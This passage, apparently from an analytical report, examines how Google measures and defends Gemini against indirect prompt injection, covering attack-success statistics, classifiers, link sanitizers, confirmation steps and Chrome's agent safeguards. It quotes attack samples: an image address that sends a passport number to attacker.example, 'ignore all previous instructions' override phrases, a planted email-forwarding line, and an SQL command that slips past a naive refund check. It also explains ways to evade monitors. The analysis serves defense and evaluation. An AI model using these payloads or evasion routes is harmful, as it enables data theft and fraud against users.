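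Google DeepMind summarizes the improvement as a 47 percent reduction in attack success. This sounds as if 47 of every 100 previously successful attacks now fail, but it is an average in percentage points. The technical report's email figures show the difference:

- Average for Gemini 2.0 Flash: (68.0 + 67.2 + 98.4) ÷ 3 = 77.9 percent
- Average for Gemini 2.5 Flash: (40.8 + 4.2 + 53.6) ÷ 3 = 32.9 percent
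- Reduction in percentage points: 77.9 − 32.9 = 45.0
- Reduction relative to the old rate: 45.0 ÷ 77.9 = 58 percent

The reported 47 is close to the third line and far from the fourth. The two-point gap from the third line is presumably due to the white paper's slightly different rates for Gemini 2.0, such as 99.8 percent instead of 98.4 for TAP. Readers who take the headline figure as a relative reduction will therefore underestimate the improvement.

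The average also makes Gemini look safer than it is, because an attacker can choose the most effective of the three methods. The best method for each model succeeds 98.4 percent of the time against 2.0 Flash and 53.6 percent against 2.5 Flash. Beam Search's success rate fell from 67.2 to 4.2 percent, which greatly improves the average but doesn't hinder an attacker who uses TAP.

The calendar result is the weakest evidence for training, because the rate fell by 5.4 points and remained close to 95 percent. Whatever Gemini learned about email did not carry over well to a similar task with a different tool, so it is risky to treat any of these rates as a general property of the model, especially as Google keeps connecting the assistant to more tools.

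A more capable model isn't necessarily safer, either. Gemini 1.5 Flash had a TAP rate of 82.2 percent, so version 2.0 was more vulnerable to persuasive language, even though it resisted the other two methods better. According to Google, a model that is better at following elaborate language also gives attackers more to exploit. Google attributes the smaller 2.0 Flash-Lite's lower rates under Actor Critic and TAP to its limited ability, not better defenses.

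The technical report applies this explanation to Gemini 2.5 Pro, the larger model, which Google considers less resilient than Flash because its greater capability still limits the protections. The table only partly supports this, since Pro does much worse than Flash under Beam Search and Actor Critic but better under TAP. The most successful attack on Pro works 63.8 percent of the time, compared with 53.6 percent for Flash. Still, both models resisted all three methods better than their 1.5 predecessors, despite being more capable, and Google credits adversarial training for this.

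### The same model on a fixed test

The white paper also reports a test with a fixed set of injections, whose success rate fell by about four-fifths, from 92 percent with Gemini 2.0 to 18 percent with 2.5. When the attacker could search for new triggers, the email attack with TAP succeeded 53.6 percent of the time, almost three times as often. Publishing only the fixed test would therefore have led readers to overestimate how much protection the training provided.

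Hardening therefore helps a great deal against attackers who reuse old triggers, as many do because it takes little effort, but much less against attackers who tailor their attacks to this model. A published robustness score means little unless the publisher also describes the attacker.

### Adding a warning to the prompt

Combining training with *Warning*, one of the simpler add-on defenses, produced the lowest attack success rates. *Warning* puts a written caution into the prompt. With it, attacks succeeded 10.8 percent of the time against Gemini 2.0 and 6.2 percent against Gemini 2.5.

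With the warning in place, moving to the trained model lowered the attack success rate by 4.6 percentage points, eliminating about 43 percent of the attacks that still worked. The training was useful, but the warning alone had already brought Gemini 2.0's rate fairly low. That is surprising, because nothing forces the model to follow the warning, and it is a good reason to test simple defenses properly before dismissing them.

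An independent study, *INFUSE* (Nguyen, Guo and colleagues, 2026), also found that security instructions in the prompt can help a lot. It tested agents that do software work by typing commands into a terminal. On a subset of cases in which attacks often succeeded, adding the instructions cut the average attack success rate from 58.2 to 14.3 percent. The side effects varied by model. Some agents became worse at their assigned tasks, and a warning may make some models refuse ordinary work.

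A 6.2 percent rate is low for a test of this kind but high for a product with many users. The trigger is designed to work across different conversations, so an attacker can send the same email to everyone. If 10,000 people received it, had conversations like those in the test, and asked the assistant for a summary, the expected number of leaked passport numbers would be 620 (10,000 × 0.062).

Far fewer people would meet those conditions in practice. If one recipient in 20 had given the assistant such a secret and then asked for a summary in the same conversation, the expected number would be 31. The test also left out the safeguards Google adds around Gemini in its products. A filter that detects the email once can block every other copy, and the assistant may ask the user before sending anything. The 620 is therefore an estimate for a model with a warning in its prompt but without these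 safeguards, and doesn't predict what would happen in Gmail.

In Anthropic's browser tests of Claude Opus 4.8, which VentureBeat compared with other companies' disclosures in 2026, professional attackers succeeded in 31.5 percent of attempts against the model without product safeguards and 0.5 percent with them. Google's safeguards may not achieve a similar reduction, but the results show that a model's score without safeguards can be a poor guide to the risk in a finished product. The product may be safer because of its safeguards, or riskier if it gives the model more tools than the test did.

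### Whether Gemini became less useful

The improvement in Gemini 2.5 is useful only if the model still does what users ask. Google DeepMind says hardening did not significantly affect the model's performance on normal tasks.

The technical report offers some support for this. Google used automated attackers to look for unhelpful responses as well as dangerous ones. The rate of helpfulness violations fell from 8.1 percent for Gemini 2.0 Flash to 6.6 percent for 2.5 Flash, and was 6.1 percent for 2.5 Pro. Google calls the two 2.5 models its most helpful to date. If adversarial training had made Gemini overcautious in general, these rates should have reflected it.

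But the two generations differ in many ways besides security training. The training could have made Gemini 2.5 slightly less helpful while other improvements raised its overall score. To isolate the training's effect, researchers would compare versions of the same model with and without it.

A model that has learned to distrust instructions in attachments may leave a form blank when the user wanted it filled in. Testing requests like this would measure the side effects of hardening better than a general helpfulness score does. Google's claim is plausible, but a drop in helpfulness violations across a whole model generation is fairly weak evidence for it.

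### Gemini 3 and later models

For later models, Google mostly describes its progress without numbers. Google DeepMind's *Gemini 3 Pro Model Card* (November 2025) reports that the company used automated red teaming to look for safety and security problems, but it gives no success rate for prompt injection. It lists vulnerability to *jailbreaks* as a main risk, "improved compared to Gemini 2.5 Pro but still an open research problem". A jailbreak is a user's attempt to make the model break its own rules, whereas the user is the victim of an indirect injection. Progress against jailbreaks may also help against injections, but the card's claim doesn't show how much.

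Google also publishes separate risk assessments for its most advanced models. Google DeepMind's *Gemini 3 Pro Frontier Safety Framework Report* (2025) covers weapons of mass destruction, cybersecurity, machine-learning research, harmful manipulation and, on an exploratory basis, misalignment. It does not cover prompt injection. Its cybersecurity section concerns the help Gemini could give an attacker, so readers can't use it to judge how well Gemini resists attacks.

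VentureBeat looked for an injection rate in Google's documents on Gemini 3 and found only a general claim of increased resistance. According to VentureBeat, OpenAI had published a score for one setting, and Anthropic had reported results for four settings, with separate figures for repeated attempts. OpenAI's and Anthropic's numbers aren't comparable, because OpenAI tested with known attacks and Anthropic used an attacker that adapted.

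Google DeepMind's *Gemini 3.7 Flash*, another model card, mentions continuing work on jailbreak resistance among the model's known limitations. In its April 2026 post on Workspace, Google says it is "continuously improving" its models' resistance to indirect injection. No scores comparable to those from the 2025 tests have been found for Gemini 3, 3.5 or 4, so it is impossible to say whether the figures of 53.6 percent for email and 94.6 percent for calendars have changed in later models.

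The security company Gray Swan AI ran a public competition in which 464 people attacked 13 models across 41 scenarios. According to its paper *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (2026), 8,648 of the 272,000 attempts succeeded, or about 3 percent. The success rate was highest against Gemini 2.5 Pro, which had gone through Google's adversarial training, at 8.5 percent, and lowest against Claude Opus 4.5, at 0.5 percent.

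The competition's 8.5 percent success rate against Gemini 2.5 Pro is not directly comparable to the 61.4 percent that Google measured for the same model with Actor Critic. The competition counted every attempt, including failed first drafts, while Google reported only the best trigger after a long search. The competition's ranking of models is more informative. People who could choose any strategy succeeded more often against Gemini 2.5 Pro than against any of the other 12 models, so any resistance it gained from training did not put it ahead of its competitors.

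Two independent tests include models from the Gemini 3 generation. Nguyen and colleagues measured an attack success rate of 23.2 percent for Gemini 2.5 Flash and 20.2 percent for a preview of Gemini 3 Flash. The Gemini 3 Flash figure comes from only 94 runs, in which about 19 attacks succeeded. Even if the runs were independent, its margin of error would be about eight percentage points either way, so the difference between the two models could easily be chance.

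A preview of Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite did much worse, with a rate of 41.9 percent, the highest among the 19 models. Google had suggested that 2.0 Flash-Lite was harder to attack in some ways because it was less capable. Any such protection did not extend to this newer small model in terminal work. These agents had broad access to a computer, and the attacks included stealing keys and creating administrator accounts, so the rates can't be compared directly with Google's email results.

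*DecodingTrust-Agent Platform (DTap)* (2026) tested agents with simulated attacks. In one set of tasks, with examples from legal work, indirect injections succeeded 56.3 percent of the time against Gemini 3 Pro on Google's own agent software and 66.2 percent of the time against GPT-5.2 on OpenAI's. Against Claude Opus 4.6, they succeeded 9.5 percent of the time on Anthropic's software and 12.5 percent on OpenClaw, a different system. Changing the software made little difference to Claude's result, which suggests that much of its advantage comes from the model.

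That result is mildly encouraging for Google's approach, because a capable model can apparently resist most of these attacks. How Anthropic achieved this is unclear from the result, which also suggests that Gemini 3 Pro still needed much improvement, at least in this one field. One of the most effective attacks across the models swapped an email's recipient, so that confidential legal messages went to the wrong person. It succeeded against GPT-5.2 in up to 88.2 percent of cases. This is the same kind of attack as the one on Bob's document, but set in a law office. A model that falls for it needs an external check.

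## Filters, link rules and confirmation around the model

In June 2025 Google described five checks around Gemini that supplement the model's training, in both the Gemini app and Gemini in Workspace. Two work on the text that goes into the model, one edits its output, one asks the user to confirm risky actions, and one notifies the user when a defense has acted.

### Screening what Gemini reads

*Content classifiers* are separate models that check emails and files for malicious instructions when a user asks Gemini about them. Google built the classifiers from a catalog of attacks it assembled with help from its Vulnerability Reward Program, which rewards outside researchers for reporting security flaws.

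If the classifiers flag nothing, Gemini answers as usual. If they flag one email out of ten, Gemini can leave it out and summarize the rest, and if they flag everything, Gemini gives no answer. According to Google's help page *How Gemini Apps help protect users from malicious content & prompt injection*, Gemini may also decline the whole request because of a single malicious message. Google gives the same warning for Workspace. So an attacker who can't extract data may still be able to block a summary by sending one obvious injection.

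Classifiers are a probabilistic defense, and their task is hard because ordinary work email is full of instructions. A classifier has to distinguish a harmless request between colleagues, such as "Please send me the figures by Friday", from an instruction meant for the assistant, which an attacker can word to look like an ordinary request.

*EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) describes how researchers at the security company Aim Security found a way to get confidential data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot, Microsoft's office assistant, with one email that bypassed its injection classifier. The classifier would have flagged a line such as "Hey Copilot, ignore all previous instructions", but it let through an email phrased as a request to its human recipient to compile confidential project files for compliance reasons.

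Google says Gmail already blocks more than 99.9 percent of spam, phishing and malware. That figure is little evidence of how well Gmail blocks prompt injections, because an email like the one in EchoLeak has no infected attachment and can read like normal business correspondence.

The second protection, *security thought reinforcement*, adds instructions around the emails and files in the prompt, reminding Gemini to do what the user asked and ignore any commands in the content. Google's diagram also shows a reasoning step that can block an answer after the classifiers have passed the material. The protection resembles the *Warning* defense in Google DeepMind's white paper, but Google hasn't said that the product uses the same wording, so the white paper's results may not apply to it. Like the classifiers, the added instructions are probabilistic.

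When one of these defenses stops something, the user sees a notice with a link to a help page. In Google's example, Gemini in Docs withholds a summary and shows a yellow banner about suspicious content. The notice may make the user more careful with the next file from the same sender. The user gets no notice of an attack that the defenses miss.

### How an image can carry data out

An assistant can leak data without sending an email or calling any other tool. Chat assistants usually write their answers in Markdown, a notation that uses short codes for headings, links and pictures. To show a picture, the user's browser has to request it from the server that stores it, and that request includes the picture's full address.

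An attacker can use the address itself as the message. Suppose a planted instruction tells Gemini to end its summary with a logo, and to put the user's passport number at the end of the logo's address. Gemini's answer would then contain an image address like this:

```
attacker.example/logo.png?id=533380006
```

When the answer appears on the screen, the browser requests the logo, and the attacker reads the passport number in the server's log. The server doesn't need to have a logo, and without one the user sees at worst a broken image. Security researchers call this a *zero-click* attack because the user never has to click.

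Google's third protection blocks this path with a rule. Software called a *sanitizer* processes Gemini's answer before the app displays it and does not render images with external addresses. The browser therefore doesn't request the logo, so the attacker's server doesn't receive the number. This works even if Gemini has followed the planted instruction, because the rule doesn't depend on detecting a malicious image or a successful injection.

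This makes the rule deterministic, but deterministic rules can have gaps, and EchoLeak exploited two in Microsoft's Copilot. Microsoft's software removed external links from Copilot's answers, but only if they were in the usual Markdown form. It missed the researchers' link, which used a less common form where the address is on a separate line below the text. Copilot's pages also restricted images to a list of approved sources. One approved source was a Microsoft Teams service that would fetch any other address on request, so the researchers sent the data through it. Microsoft fixed the flaw in May 2025, and according to Reddy and Gujral there was no evidence that criminals had used it.

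EchoLeak became public on 11 June 2025. Two days later, Google wrote that this kind of attack was "not applicable to Gemini" because the sanitizer doesn't render external images. The claim is reasonable because refusing all external images leaves fewer openings than keeping a list of approved ones. But it holds only if the sanitizer recognizes every way of embedding an image and no address it treats as internal forwards requests to outside servers.

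Links are harder to deal with than images. They can carry data in the same way, although the user has to click. *Trust No AI* (2024) describes a February 2024 attack on Copilot in which an injected email made the assistant search the user's inbox and hide what it found in a link, using invisible characters. It also reports that Amazon solved a similar problem in its business assistant by not rendering links at all.

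Google still shows links, which people often want in a summary, and removes only those it considers suspicious, leaving the user with the words "suspicious link removed". Detection relies on Google Safe Browsing, the company's service for identifying dangerous websites. Software can remove every flagged link, but an attacker may avoid being flagged by using a new website with no bad history. *Invitation Is All You Need* (2025) describes injection attacks on Gemini that researchers reported to Google in February 2025. Google says it improved its detection after that report and that internal tests confirmed the improvement, but the statement it gave the researchers contains no figures.

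### Asking the user

Google's fourth protection in June 2025 had Gemini ask for confirmation before certain actions. In Google's example, the user asks Gemini to delete all of Saturday's events. Gemini lists the three it finds in the calendar, with their details, and deletes them only if the user agrees. The list gives the user a chance to notice that one of the events is a flight.

Confirmation has become more important as Gemini's abilities have grown. Google's *Use Gemini Agent for multi-step tasks in Gemini Apps* describes a feature that can carry out multi-step tasks in a browser and in connected apps. Gemini is "designed to ask" before it sends messages, changes the user's data, buys something or submits a web form. The user can confirm or decline each task, or confirm all of them with one button. The button saves time, but it also lets the user approve a harmful step along with several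 harmless ones in a single click.

Gemini Spark, a newer agent in the Gemini app, can also run tasks on a schedule. Google's *Use Gemini Spark to manage your tasks and workflows in Gemini Apps* lists nearly the same actions as needing confirmation and says users must also review planned edits to shared documents. Google warns that a user who is offline when a scheduled task runs may be unable to stop an unintended action, and it advises against scheduling anything sensitive. It says its own safeguards do not guarantee safety and calls the user's active supervision the most important protection, which is a lot to expect of people who use the agent so that they don't have to supervise the work.

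Google offers companies firmer rules. *Defend against agentic risks with multi-layered protections in Google Workspace Studio* (Quinney, 2026) describes a tool that employees use to set up automated sequences of steps, called flows. An administrator can require a flow's owner to approve any email to recipients outside the company. Software can check whether an address belongs to the company's domain, so no model has to judge whether the email looks risky.

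Google is imposing a similar requirement on other companies' agents. Help Net Security's *Google mandates MCP or CLI access for Workspace AI agents* (2026) reports that, from 1 February 2027, these agents must connect to Workspace through interfaces that enforce user confirmation before an agent sends an email, changes who can open a file, or edits many items at once. Two Google executives wrote that such checks "have to live in the request path". A prompt injection can't make an agent skip a confirmation that the mail service itself enforces. For Gemini's own agents, the phrase "designed to ask" doesn't specify whether ordinary software or a model decides when to request confirmation.

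### Quick fixes and slower retraining

By April 2026, Google was also describing how it updates these defenses. In Workspace, a central *Policy Engine* controls the deterministic ones. Gavish lists settings for basic tool calls, cleaning up web addresses, and *tool chaining*, which presumably means rules about which tool calls may follow others. He gives no example, but such a rule might stop Gemini from opening an outside web page right after reading private email, or require the user's confirmation first.

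A tool-chaining rule could block steps that look harmless individually but are harmful in combination. For example, an attacker could steal data by getting Gemini to read an email and then open a web page. But a rule that considers only the order of the tools would also block honest requests that need the same two steps, such as checking a parcel's delivery status from the link in a confirmation email.

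The Policy Engine's main advantage is speed. When Google learns of a new attack, engineers can block it by changing a setting, without waiting to retrain a model. Gavish calls these changes "point fixes" and gives the example of a *regex takedown*. A regex, or regular expression, is a pattern that software compares with text, so engineers could use one to block every address with the unusual structure that an attack relies on. An attacker can get past the pattern by changing the structure, but the fix gives Google time to work on a more general defense.

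That work begins with a catalog of attacks collected from Google's own testers, automated attack programs, outside researchers, and public reports. Staff reproduce each attack, check whether it is already in the catalog, and assign it to the team responsible. A system called Simula then generates variants. For example, it might turn one malicious calendar invitation into hundreds with different wording, senders, and goals.

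Engineers use some of these variants to retrain the classifiers and hold back others to test them. They also use the variants to improve the written instructions of defenses that rely on a language model, and to train Gemini itself. Testing on the held-back variants shows whether a classifier has learned more than the exact texts in its training data. But both groups come from the same known attacks, so the test doesn't show how well a classifier handles new kinds of attack. The tests of Gemini's own training have the same limitation.

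### Protections for longer tasks

Google's latest post on defense in depth concerns tasks in which Gemini browses websites, runs code and works with the user's files. In Google's example, a user asks Gemini why their $389 electric bill is so high. Gemini has to look through old bills in the user's email, sign in to the utility's website, and compare hourly usage with the utility's prices. It finds that the heat pump starts at 4 p.m., when electricity is most expensive.

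Gemini does the browsing and the calculations in a *microVM*, a small virtual machine isolated from other machines by hardware. If Gemini opens an infected file or runs a bad script, the damage should stay inside that machine. EconoTimes' *Google Cloud Plans Preview of Isolated Agent Compute Engine* (2026) reports that the service can suspend an idle machine and restore it later, which suits tasks that have to wait for the user. The isolation doesn't depend on a model's judgment, but it protects only the computer. Gemini still needs access to the user's email to find the old bills, and an attacker can try to misuse that access through an injection from inside the machine.

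Classifiers scan search results, web pages, emails and files before they reach the *planner*, the model that chooses Gemini's next action. Model-level checks then look for signs of injection while Gemini reads, and are meant to make it treat the content as information rather than instructions. Both are updated versions of the 2025 defenses, and both are probabilistic.

The link rules have changed more. In 2025, the danger was that the user's browser would request an address from Gemini's answer. An agent with its own browser can open the address without showing it to the user. Google therefore also applies deterministic rules to which addresses Gemini may open and which outside services it may send information to. If a fake promotional email contains instructions to add details of the user's bills to a link and open it, the rules can block the request even if the classifiers and the model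 have both failed to stop the attack.

How well this works depends on which addresses the rules allow, and Google doesn't publish the rules. A short list of approved sites would be very safe, but an agent limited to it couldn't look up an unfamiliar utility company. A looser rule would let Gemini use more of the web but also give an attacker more places to receive data. Spark's help page says Gemini limits its browsing to sites relevant to the task. That would be a compromise, but software can't easily decide what is relevant without help from a model.

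*Policy Guardian* checks the commands that Gemini runs in its virtual machine, the scripts they refer to, and changes to files. Deterministic rules quickly approve routine operations, and a language model makes a probabilistic judgment about unclear or riskier ones by comparing them with the user's request and the session history. Policy Guardian can block a command, ask the user, or send Gemini an explanation so that it tries a safer method.

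Google presents Policy Guardian mainly as protection against Gemini's own mistakes. For example, if a step fails, Gemini might try to work around it by deleting far more files than necessary. The same check would help if an injection caused the deletion. But the session history may contain text from emails and web pages that Gemini has read, and if the judging model receives that text, an attacker could try to influence its decision too.

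The *Action Safety Agent* does a similar job for websites and connected apps. It rejects some tasks at the start, such as sending spam or buying goods in bulk. Just before Gemini changes something outside its virtual machine, the agent compares the user's original request, the steps so far, and the exact details of the action. If the action would have real consequences, the agent asks the user to confirm. It does this even when the user has chosen "Always allow" for the tool or site, so an old permission doesn't automatically cover a new, more harmful action.

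The Action Safety Agent almost certainly relies on a language model, because it has to understand a request in ordinary language and compare it with a proposed action. Its decisions would therefore be probabilistic. In Chrome, Google keeps the model that reviews actions away from untrusted content. Google doesn't mention such a separation in its description of the Action Safety Agent, and the steps taken so far could easily include text that an attacker wrote.

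When Gemini reaches a page that asks the user to sign in or open an account, it stops and gives the user control of the browser. The user types the password and returns control. In the United States, Google's password manager can fill in the password on sites the user has approved, without showing it to the model. Because Gemini never has the password, an injection can't make Gemini reveal it. Once the user has signed in, though, Gemini can use the account, so the remaining protections have to prevent harmful actions there.

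### What is in use, and what is measured

Google distinguishes only loosely between protections in use and those still to come. In June 2025, it said it was "in the process of rolling out" the classifiers and described the other four protections as already part of Gemini. It also promised more defenses later that year without naming them. Gavish describes retraining the classifiers as an established routine, which suggests that they were in use in Workspace by April 2026, but Google doesn't appear to have announced when the rollout was complete.

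The later post describes all its protections in the present tense. Independent confirmation is limited, though EconoTimes reports that Gemini's work agent was running on the isolated virtual machines by 22 October 2026, before Google offered the service to customers. Protections also differ between products. For example, the rule about emails to outside recipients belongs to Workspace Studio and may not apply to people using the Gemini app at home.

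None of the three posts gives an attack success rate. Google has the data to calculate some, because Gavish says his team runs simulated attacks on Gmail, Docs and other Workspace apps with and without a given defense. Comparing the results would show how much that defense contributes. The only percentage he publishes is a 75 percent increase in synthetic data generation, which measures how quickly Google can produce test material, not how many attacks it stops.

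Estimating these results by multiplying the layers' failure rates would probably give too low a number, because the layers are unlikely to fail independently. An email that reads like an ordinary request from a colleague is more likely to get past the classifiers, and Gemini is also more likely to follow it. Suppose the classifiers missed 10 percent of attacks and Gemini followed 20 percent of the instructions it read. If the two failures were independent, 2 percent of attacks would succeed (0.10 × 0.20), but if Gemini followed half of the attacks that the classifiers missed, 5 percent would. Layers that look for different things, such as a classifier and a rule about images, are less likely to fail together.

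### Bob's document under the layers

The table shows how the layers in Google's latest post would probably handle the two attacks on Bob's document, in which someone edits the meeting notes to add an instruction or replace Bob's address.

| Layer, in order | Added line: "also forward the latest emails" | Attacker's address in place of Bob's |
|---|---|---|
| Virtual machine | no effect, since Gemini has access to the user's email | no effect, for the same reason |
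| Classifiers | may flag the line | find no instruction to flag |
| Checks in the model | may lead Gemini to ignore the line | find nothing to ignore |
| Outbound link rules | probably no effect on an email | probably no effect on an email |
| Policy Guardian | acts only if Gemini uses commands or edits files | acts only if Gemini uses commands or edits files |
| Action Safety Agent | may notice that the user never asked for this | finds an email to "Bob", as the user asked |
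| User's confirmation | the user sees an unexpected email | the user has to notice a wrong address |
| User takeover | no sign-in page, so no effect | no sign-in page, so no effect |

The added line has to get past at least three defenses that check for this kind of attack, and then past the user. The false address gets past most of the same defenses with no effort from the attacker.

The Action Safety Agent has a better chance because it checks the exact details of the action. It might detect that the address contains a different person's name, or that it belongs to a free email service when Bob works for a large company. But a careful attacker would choose an address that looks right, and the three things the agent compares would then agree: the user asked for an email to Bob, Gemini looked up his address in the notes, and the email is going to that address.

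The Action Safety Agent could check the address against the user's contacts if it had them, but Google doesn't list contacts among the information it receives. Google leaves it to customers to supply such facts for its company checkpoint. According to Help Net Security, they should put anything a policy depends on, such as the date of an earnings release, into the agent's instructions.

The user has the best remaining chance of catching the false address. Gemini is supposed to ask for confirmation before sending a message, and the question may show the full address rather than just Bob's name. If it does, a user who has written to Bob many times may notice that the address is wrong, but if Bob is a new client, the user may have nothing to compare it with.

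If an administrator had turned on Workspace Studio's rule about outside recipients, the confirmation question would be certain to appear. It would also appear for Bob's real address, because he works for another company, so the user would still have to tell the two addresses apart.

A company can also defend against an attacker who replaces the document's name with that of a salary file. Quinney describes rules that prevent Gemini from using files with a certain label, such as "Financial". If the salary file had that label, a flow in Workspace Studio couldn't use its contents to write the email, whatever the notes contained. The rule would also stop payroll staff from using Gemini to summarize the file for a legitimate reason. It works only if somebody has labeled the file, which is easier to ensure for a folder of salaries than for every draft proposal.

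CaMeL would handle the false address differently because its interpreter records that the address came from notes that other people can edit. None of the layers in Google's public descriptions of the Gemini app or Workspace appears to keep such a record, though the products may contain checks that Google hasn't made public. Policy Guardian tracks the state of a session, and the tool-chaining rules may take earlier steps into account, but nothing in Google's descriptions suggests that either follows a single value from the notes to the email.

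A tool-chaining rule could come fairly close by requiring confirmation whenever Gemini sends an email after reading a shared file. But Gemini would also ask about an address the user had typed into the request, which the attacker could not have changed. If Gemini had a record of where each address came from, it could send that email without asking and request confirmation only for the address from the notes. Without that record, Google must either have Gemini ask about many harmless emails or rely on a model to pick out the dangerous ones.

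## Chrome and the middle course: separating some parts

Tagging every value, as CaMeL does, is the most exact way to tell a risky email from a harmless one. A cruder way is to track only whether the agent has just read something suspicious. In their May 2025 paper, Díaz and colleagues give the example of a rule that stops an agent from emailing outsiders right after it has processed data from a known suspicious source, unless the user approves. Willison noticed the similarity to CaMeL's data-flow tracking. The rule depends on only one fact about the session, so engineers could add it to an existing product fairly easily. But it would miss the attack on Bob's document, because a colleague's shared notes are not a known suspicious source.

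The paper argues for combining hard limits set by software with models that judge the cases rules handle badly. Google's agent in Chrome follows this approach and also borrows from CaMeL the idea of using a model that never reads the web page.

### Three principles and two layers

Díaz and colleagues want every agent to have a well-defined human controller, limited powers, and actions that people can observe.

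The principle about controllers requires the system to reliably tell the user's instructions apart from everything else the agent reads. Willison objects that nobody knows how to do this inside a prompt. The paper acknowledges this and adds that the usual way of running agents makes the problem worse. An agent that plans, acts, reads the result and plans again gives hostile text a new opportunity to influence it in every round. CaMeL avoids this by fixing the plan at the start, but Chrome's agent still plans again after reading each result.

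The paper goes further than the old security rule that a program should have only the permissions it needs. It proposes changing an agent's permissions with the task, so that an agent helping with creative writing can't delete files. Willison found this intriguing but hard to picture in practice. The only method he could think of was using more AI to adjust the permissions, and an injection could influence that AI too.

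Observability means logging what the agent reads, which tools it calls and what it sends them. It also means describing each action in advance, such as whether it only reads data or changes it. Chuvakin (2025), in *Cloud CISO Perspectives*, calls these descriptions "action manifests". In one example, a user asks an agent to set up a virtual machine, but an injection makes it try to delete every database. Software outside the model applies a rule that identifies the deletion from its manifest and blocks it.

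Google calls such software a *policy engine*, the name it also uses in Workspace. The engine can allow a tool call, block it or ask the user. In the paper's example, the engine blocks any purchase over $500 and asks the user about purchases between $100 and $500. Engineers can test and audit such a rule. But Díaz and colleagues concede that writing rules for every action is hard, and that a simple rule can't distinguish between an agent emailing a summary the user wanted and an agent stealing the document.

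The paper therefore adds a second layer of model-based defenses: adversarial training, classifiers, and models that predict whether a plan will end badly. These can take context into account, but according to the paper they are inadequate on their own for critical or irreversible actions. Willison likes the policy engine and doubts that the second layer is worth adding, but he also warns that people who get too many confirmation questions will click "yes" to all of them. A model that catches most bad emails lets the system ask for confirmation less often, which helps as long as no irreversible action depends on the model alone.

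It is unclear how much of this Google had built by May 2025. The paper says Google is already "implementing" the hybrid approach, but its abstract calls the framework aspirational. Chuvakin names one product, Google's Agentspace for businesses, whose access controls, model safeguards and logging follow the guidelines. The paper is better evidence of the goals of Google's security engineers than of the protections Gemini's users had at the time.

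### A refund rule in code

Google later published a small working example of deterministic checks outside the model. *Build zero-trust AI agents with Google's Agent Development Kit* (Saboo and Dong, 2026) describes the customer-support agent that faced the demand for a $10,000 refund. The agent signs every change to the database with a cryptographic key, so an auditor can tell which agent made it and whether anyone has altered it since. Any code the model writes runs in an isolated environment without a network connection. A gateway checks prompts and database commands against fixed rules.

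The signature doesn't stop a fooled agent, which would sign the fraudulent refund with its own valid key, so the gateway has to stop the refund. The sample code in the post does this badly. It doesn't compare the refund with the value of the order. It looks for the words "update orders" in a command and blocks the command if the text "149.00" is missing. A command like this one would pass:

```
UPDATE orders SET refund_amount = 10000.00 WHERE total = 149.00
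```

A legitimate $89 refund on another order would fail. The gateway also searches prompts for phrases such as "ignore previous instructions", but the post's sample attack begins "Ignore all previous instructions", and the extra word is enough to get it past the check.

This is teaching code, and a developer could repair the refund rule by reading both amounts as numbers and comparing them.

### The User Alignment Critic

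Gemini can act on web pages in Chrome, a feature Google calls *auto browse*. The planner reads those pages, and Parker accepts that it remains vulnerable despite training and spotlighting. Google therefore added a separate model, the *User Alignment Critic*, which doesn't read the pages.

The critic runs after the planner has chosen an action and before Chrome performs it. It uses *metadata*, or information describing the action, to check whether the action serves the user's goal. If it doesn't, the critic vetoes the action and returns feedback, and the planner tries something else. After repeated failures, the planner can return control to the user.

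Suppose a user asks the assistant to buy a T-shirt, and a review on the shop's page contains hidden text telling it to buy a gift card and message the code to a stranger. The planner may follow the hidden instructions, but the critic receives only the user's request and the proposal to buy a gift card, so it should reject the purchase. A second model that had read the same review would be a weaker check, because the text that fooled one model might fool the other.

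Google says this design is "inspired partially" by the dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL. Chrome borrows the idea of keeping one model away from untrusted content. CaMeL has that protected model write the plan, but in Chrome the model that reads untrusted content chooses every action, and the protected model can only reject its choices.

An attacker who controls the planner can therefore keep looking for a harmful action that appears to fit the task. The critic's feedback could help the attacker, since it gives a fooled planner a reason to describe the same action differently. Handing control back to the user after repeated failures should limit this, but Parker doesn't say how many failures it takes.

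In return, the planner can respond to what it finds. If the T-shirt is sold out in the user's size, the planner can look for another shop. CaMeL's privileged model would have had to write a branch for this case in advance. Chrome gives up control-flow integrity for this flexibility, so a malicious page can still change which step the planner proposes next.

Chrome has other defenses besides the critic. A classifier checks each page for injections while the planner works, and can prevent actions based on content it considers malicious. Chrome also compares addresses with a fixed list of sensitive sites, such as banks and medical portals, and requires the user's confirmation before the agent opens one. For purchases, messages and other consequential steps, Parker says only that the agent "will try to pause". Software can match a site against a list much more reliably than it can recognize every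 consequential button on the web.

### Which sites the agent may use

Browsers already separate pages by *origin*, which is roughly one website, identified by the protocol, host name and port in its address. A page from one origin generally can't read a page from another, so a malicious site can't read the mail in the next tab. An agent weakens this protection because it has to read one site and type into another. Anyone who takes control of the agent may be able to move data between all the sites where the user is signed in.

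Google designed *Agent Origin Sets* so that Chrome keeps two lists for each session, one of origins that Gemini may only read and another of origins where it may also click and type. Suppose the user wants the ingredients for a recipe added to a supermarket cart. The recipe site belongs on the read-only list and the supermarket on the read-writable list. The user's webmail belongs on neither, so an injection in the recipe can't make the agent send an email. Chrome also doesn't show the model frames that come from unlisted origins, such as advertisements. For tools other than websites, Google similarly separates calls that read from calls that write.

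The planner proposes origins, and a *gating function* checks whether they are relevant to the task. Like the critic, it doesn't receive web content. This partly answers Willison's earlier objection to adjustable permissions, because text on a web page can't influence the gating function directly. But an injection can still lead the planner to propose the attacker's site, and the attacker can choose a domain that looks relevant, such as `fresh-ingredients.example` for a recipe task.

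Parker says a variant of the critic checks whether new origins are relevant, so a model decides which origins are listed. The browser can then enforce part of the lists in code, for example by never sending the model data from an unlisted frame.

Web addresses that the model writes could contain private data, so Chrome also uses a deterministic check to restrict them to known, public addresses. The check would reject an address ending in the user's passport number because nobody has published that address.

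The agent can still leak information through its choice of known addresses. In principle, an attacker could publish a thousand pages numbered 000 to 999 and wait until Chrome treated them as known. Visits to pages 533, 380 and 006, in that order, would then give the attacker the passport number 533380006. Each choice among *N* equally likely pages conveys log₂ *N* bits, or about 10 bits for a thousand pages. The attack would work only if the gating function had already admitted the attacker's site, so the two checks together are stronger than either one alone.

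Google didn't launch all of this at once. Parker writes that the first version "just tracks the read-writeable set", because it is hard to balance security and convenience without seeing how people use the agent. He doesn't explain how that version treats sites the agent only needs to read. If Chrome puts them on the single list, the agent can also type into the recipe site. If Chrome leaves them off but still lets the agent read them, more hostile text can reach the planner. Either way, the first version protects less than the full design.

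### From the design to the product

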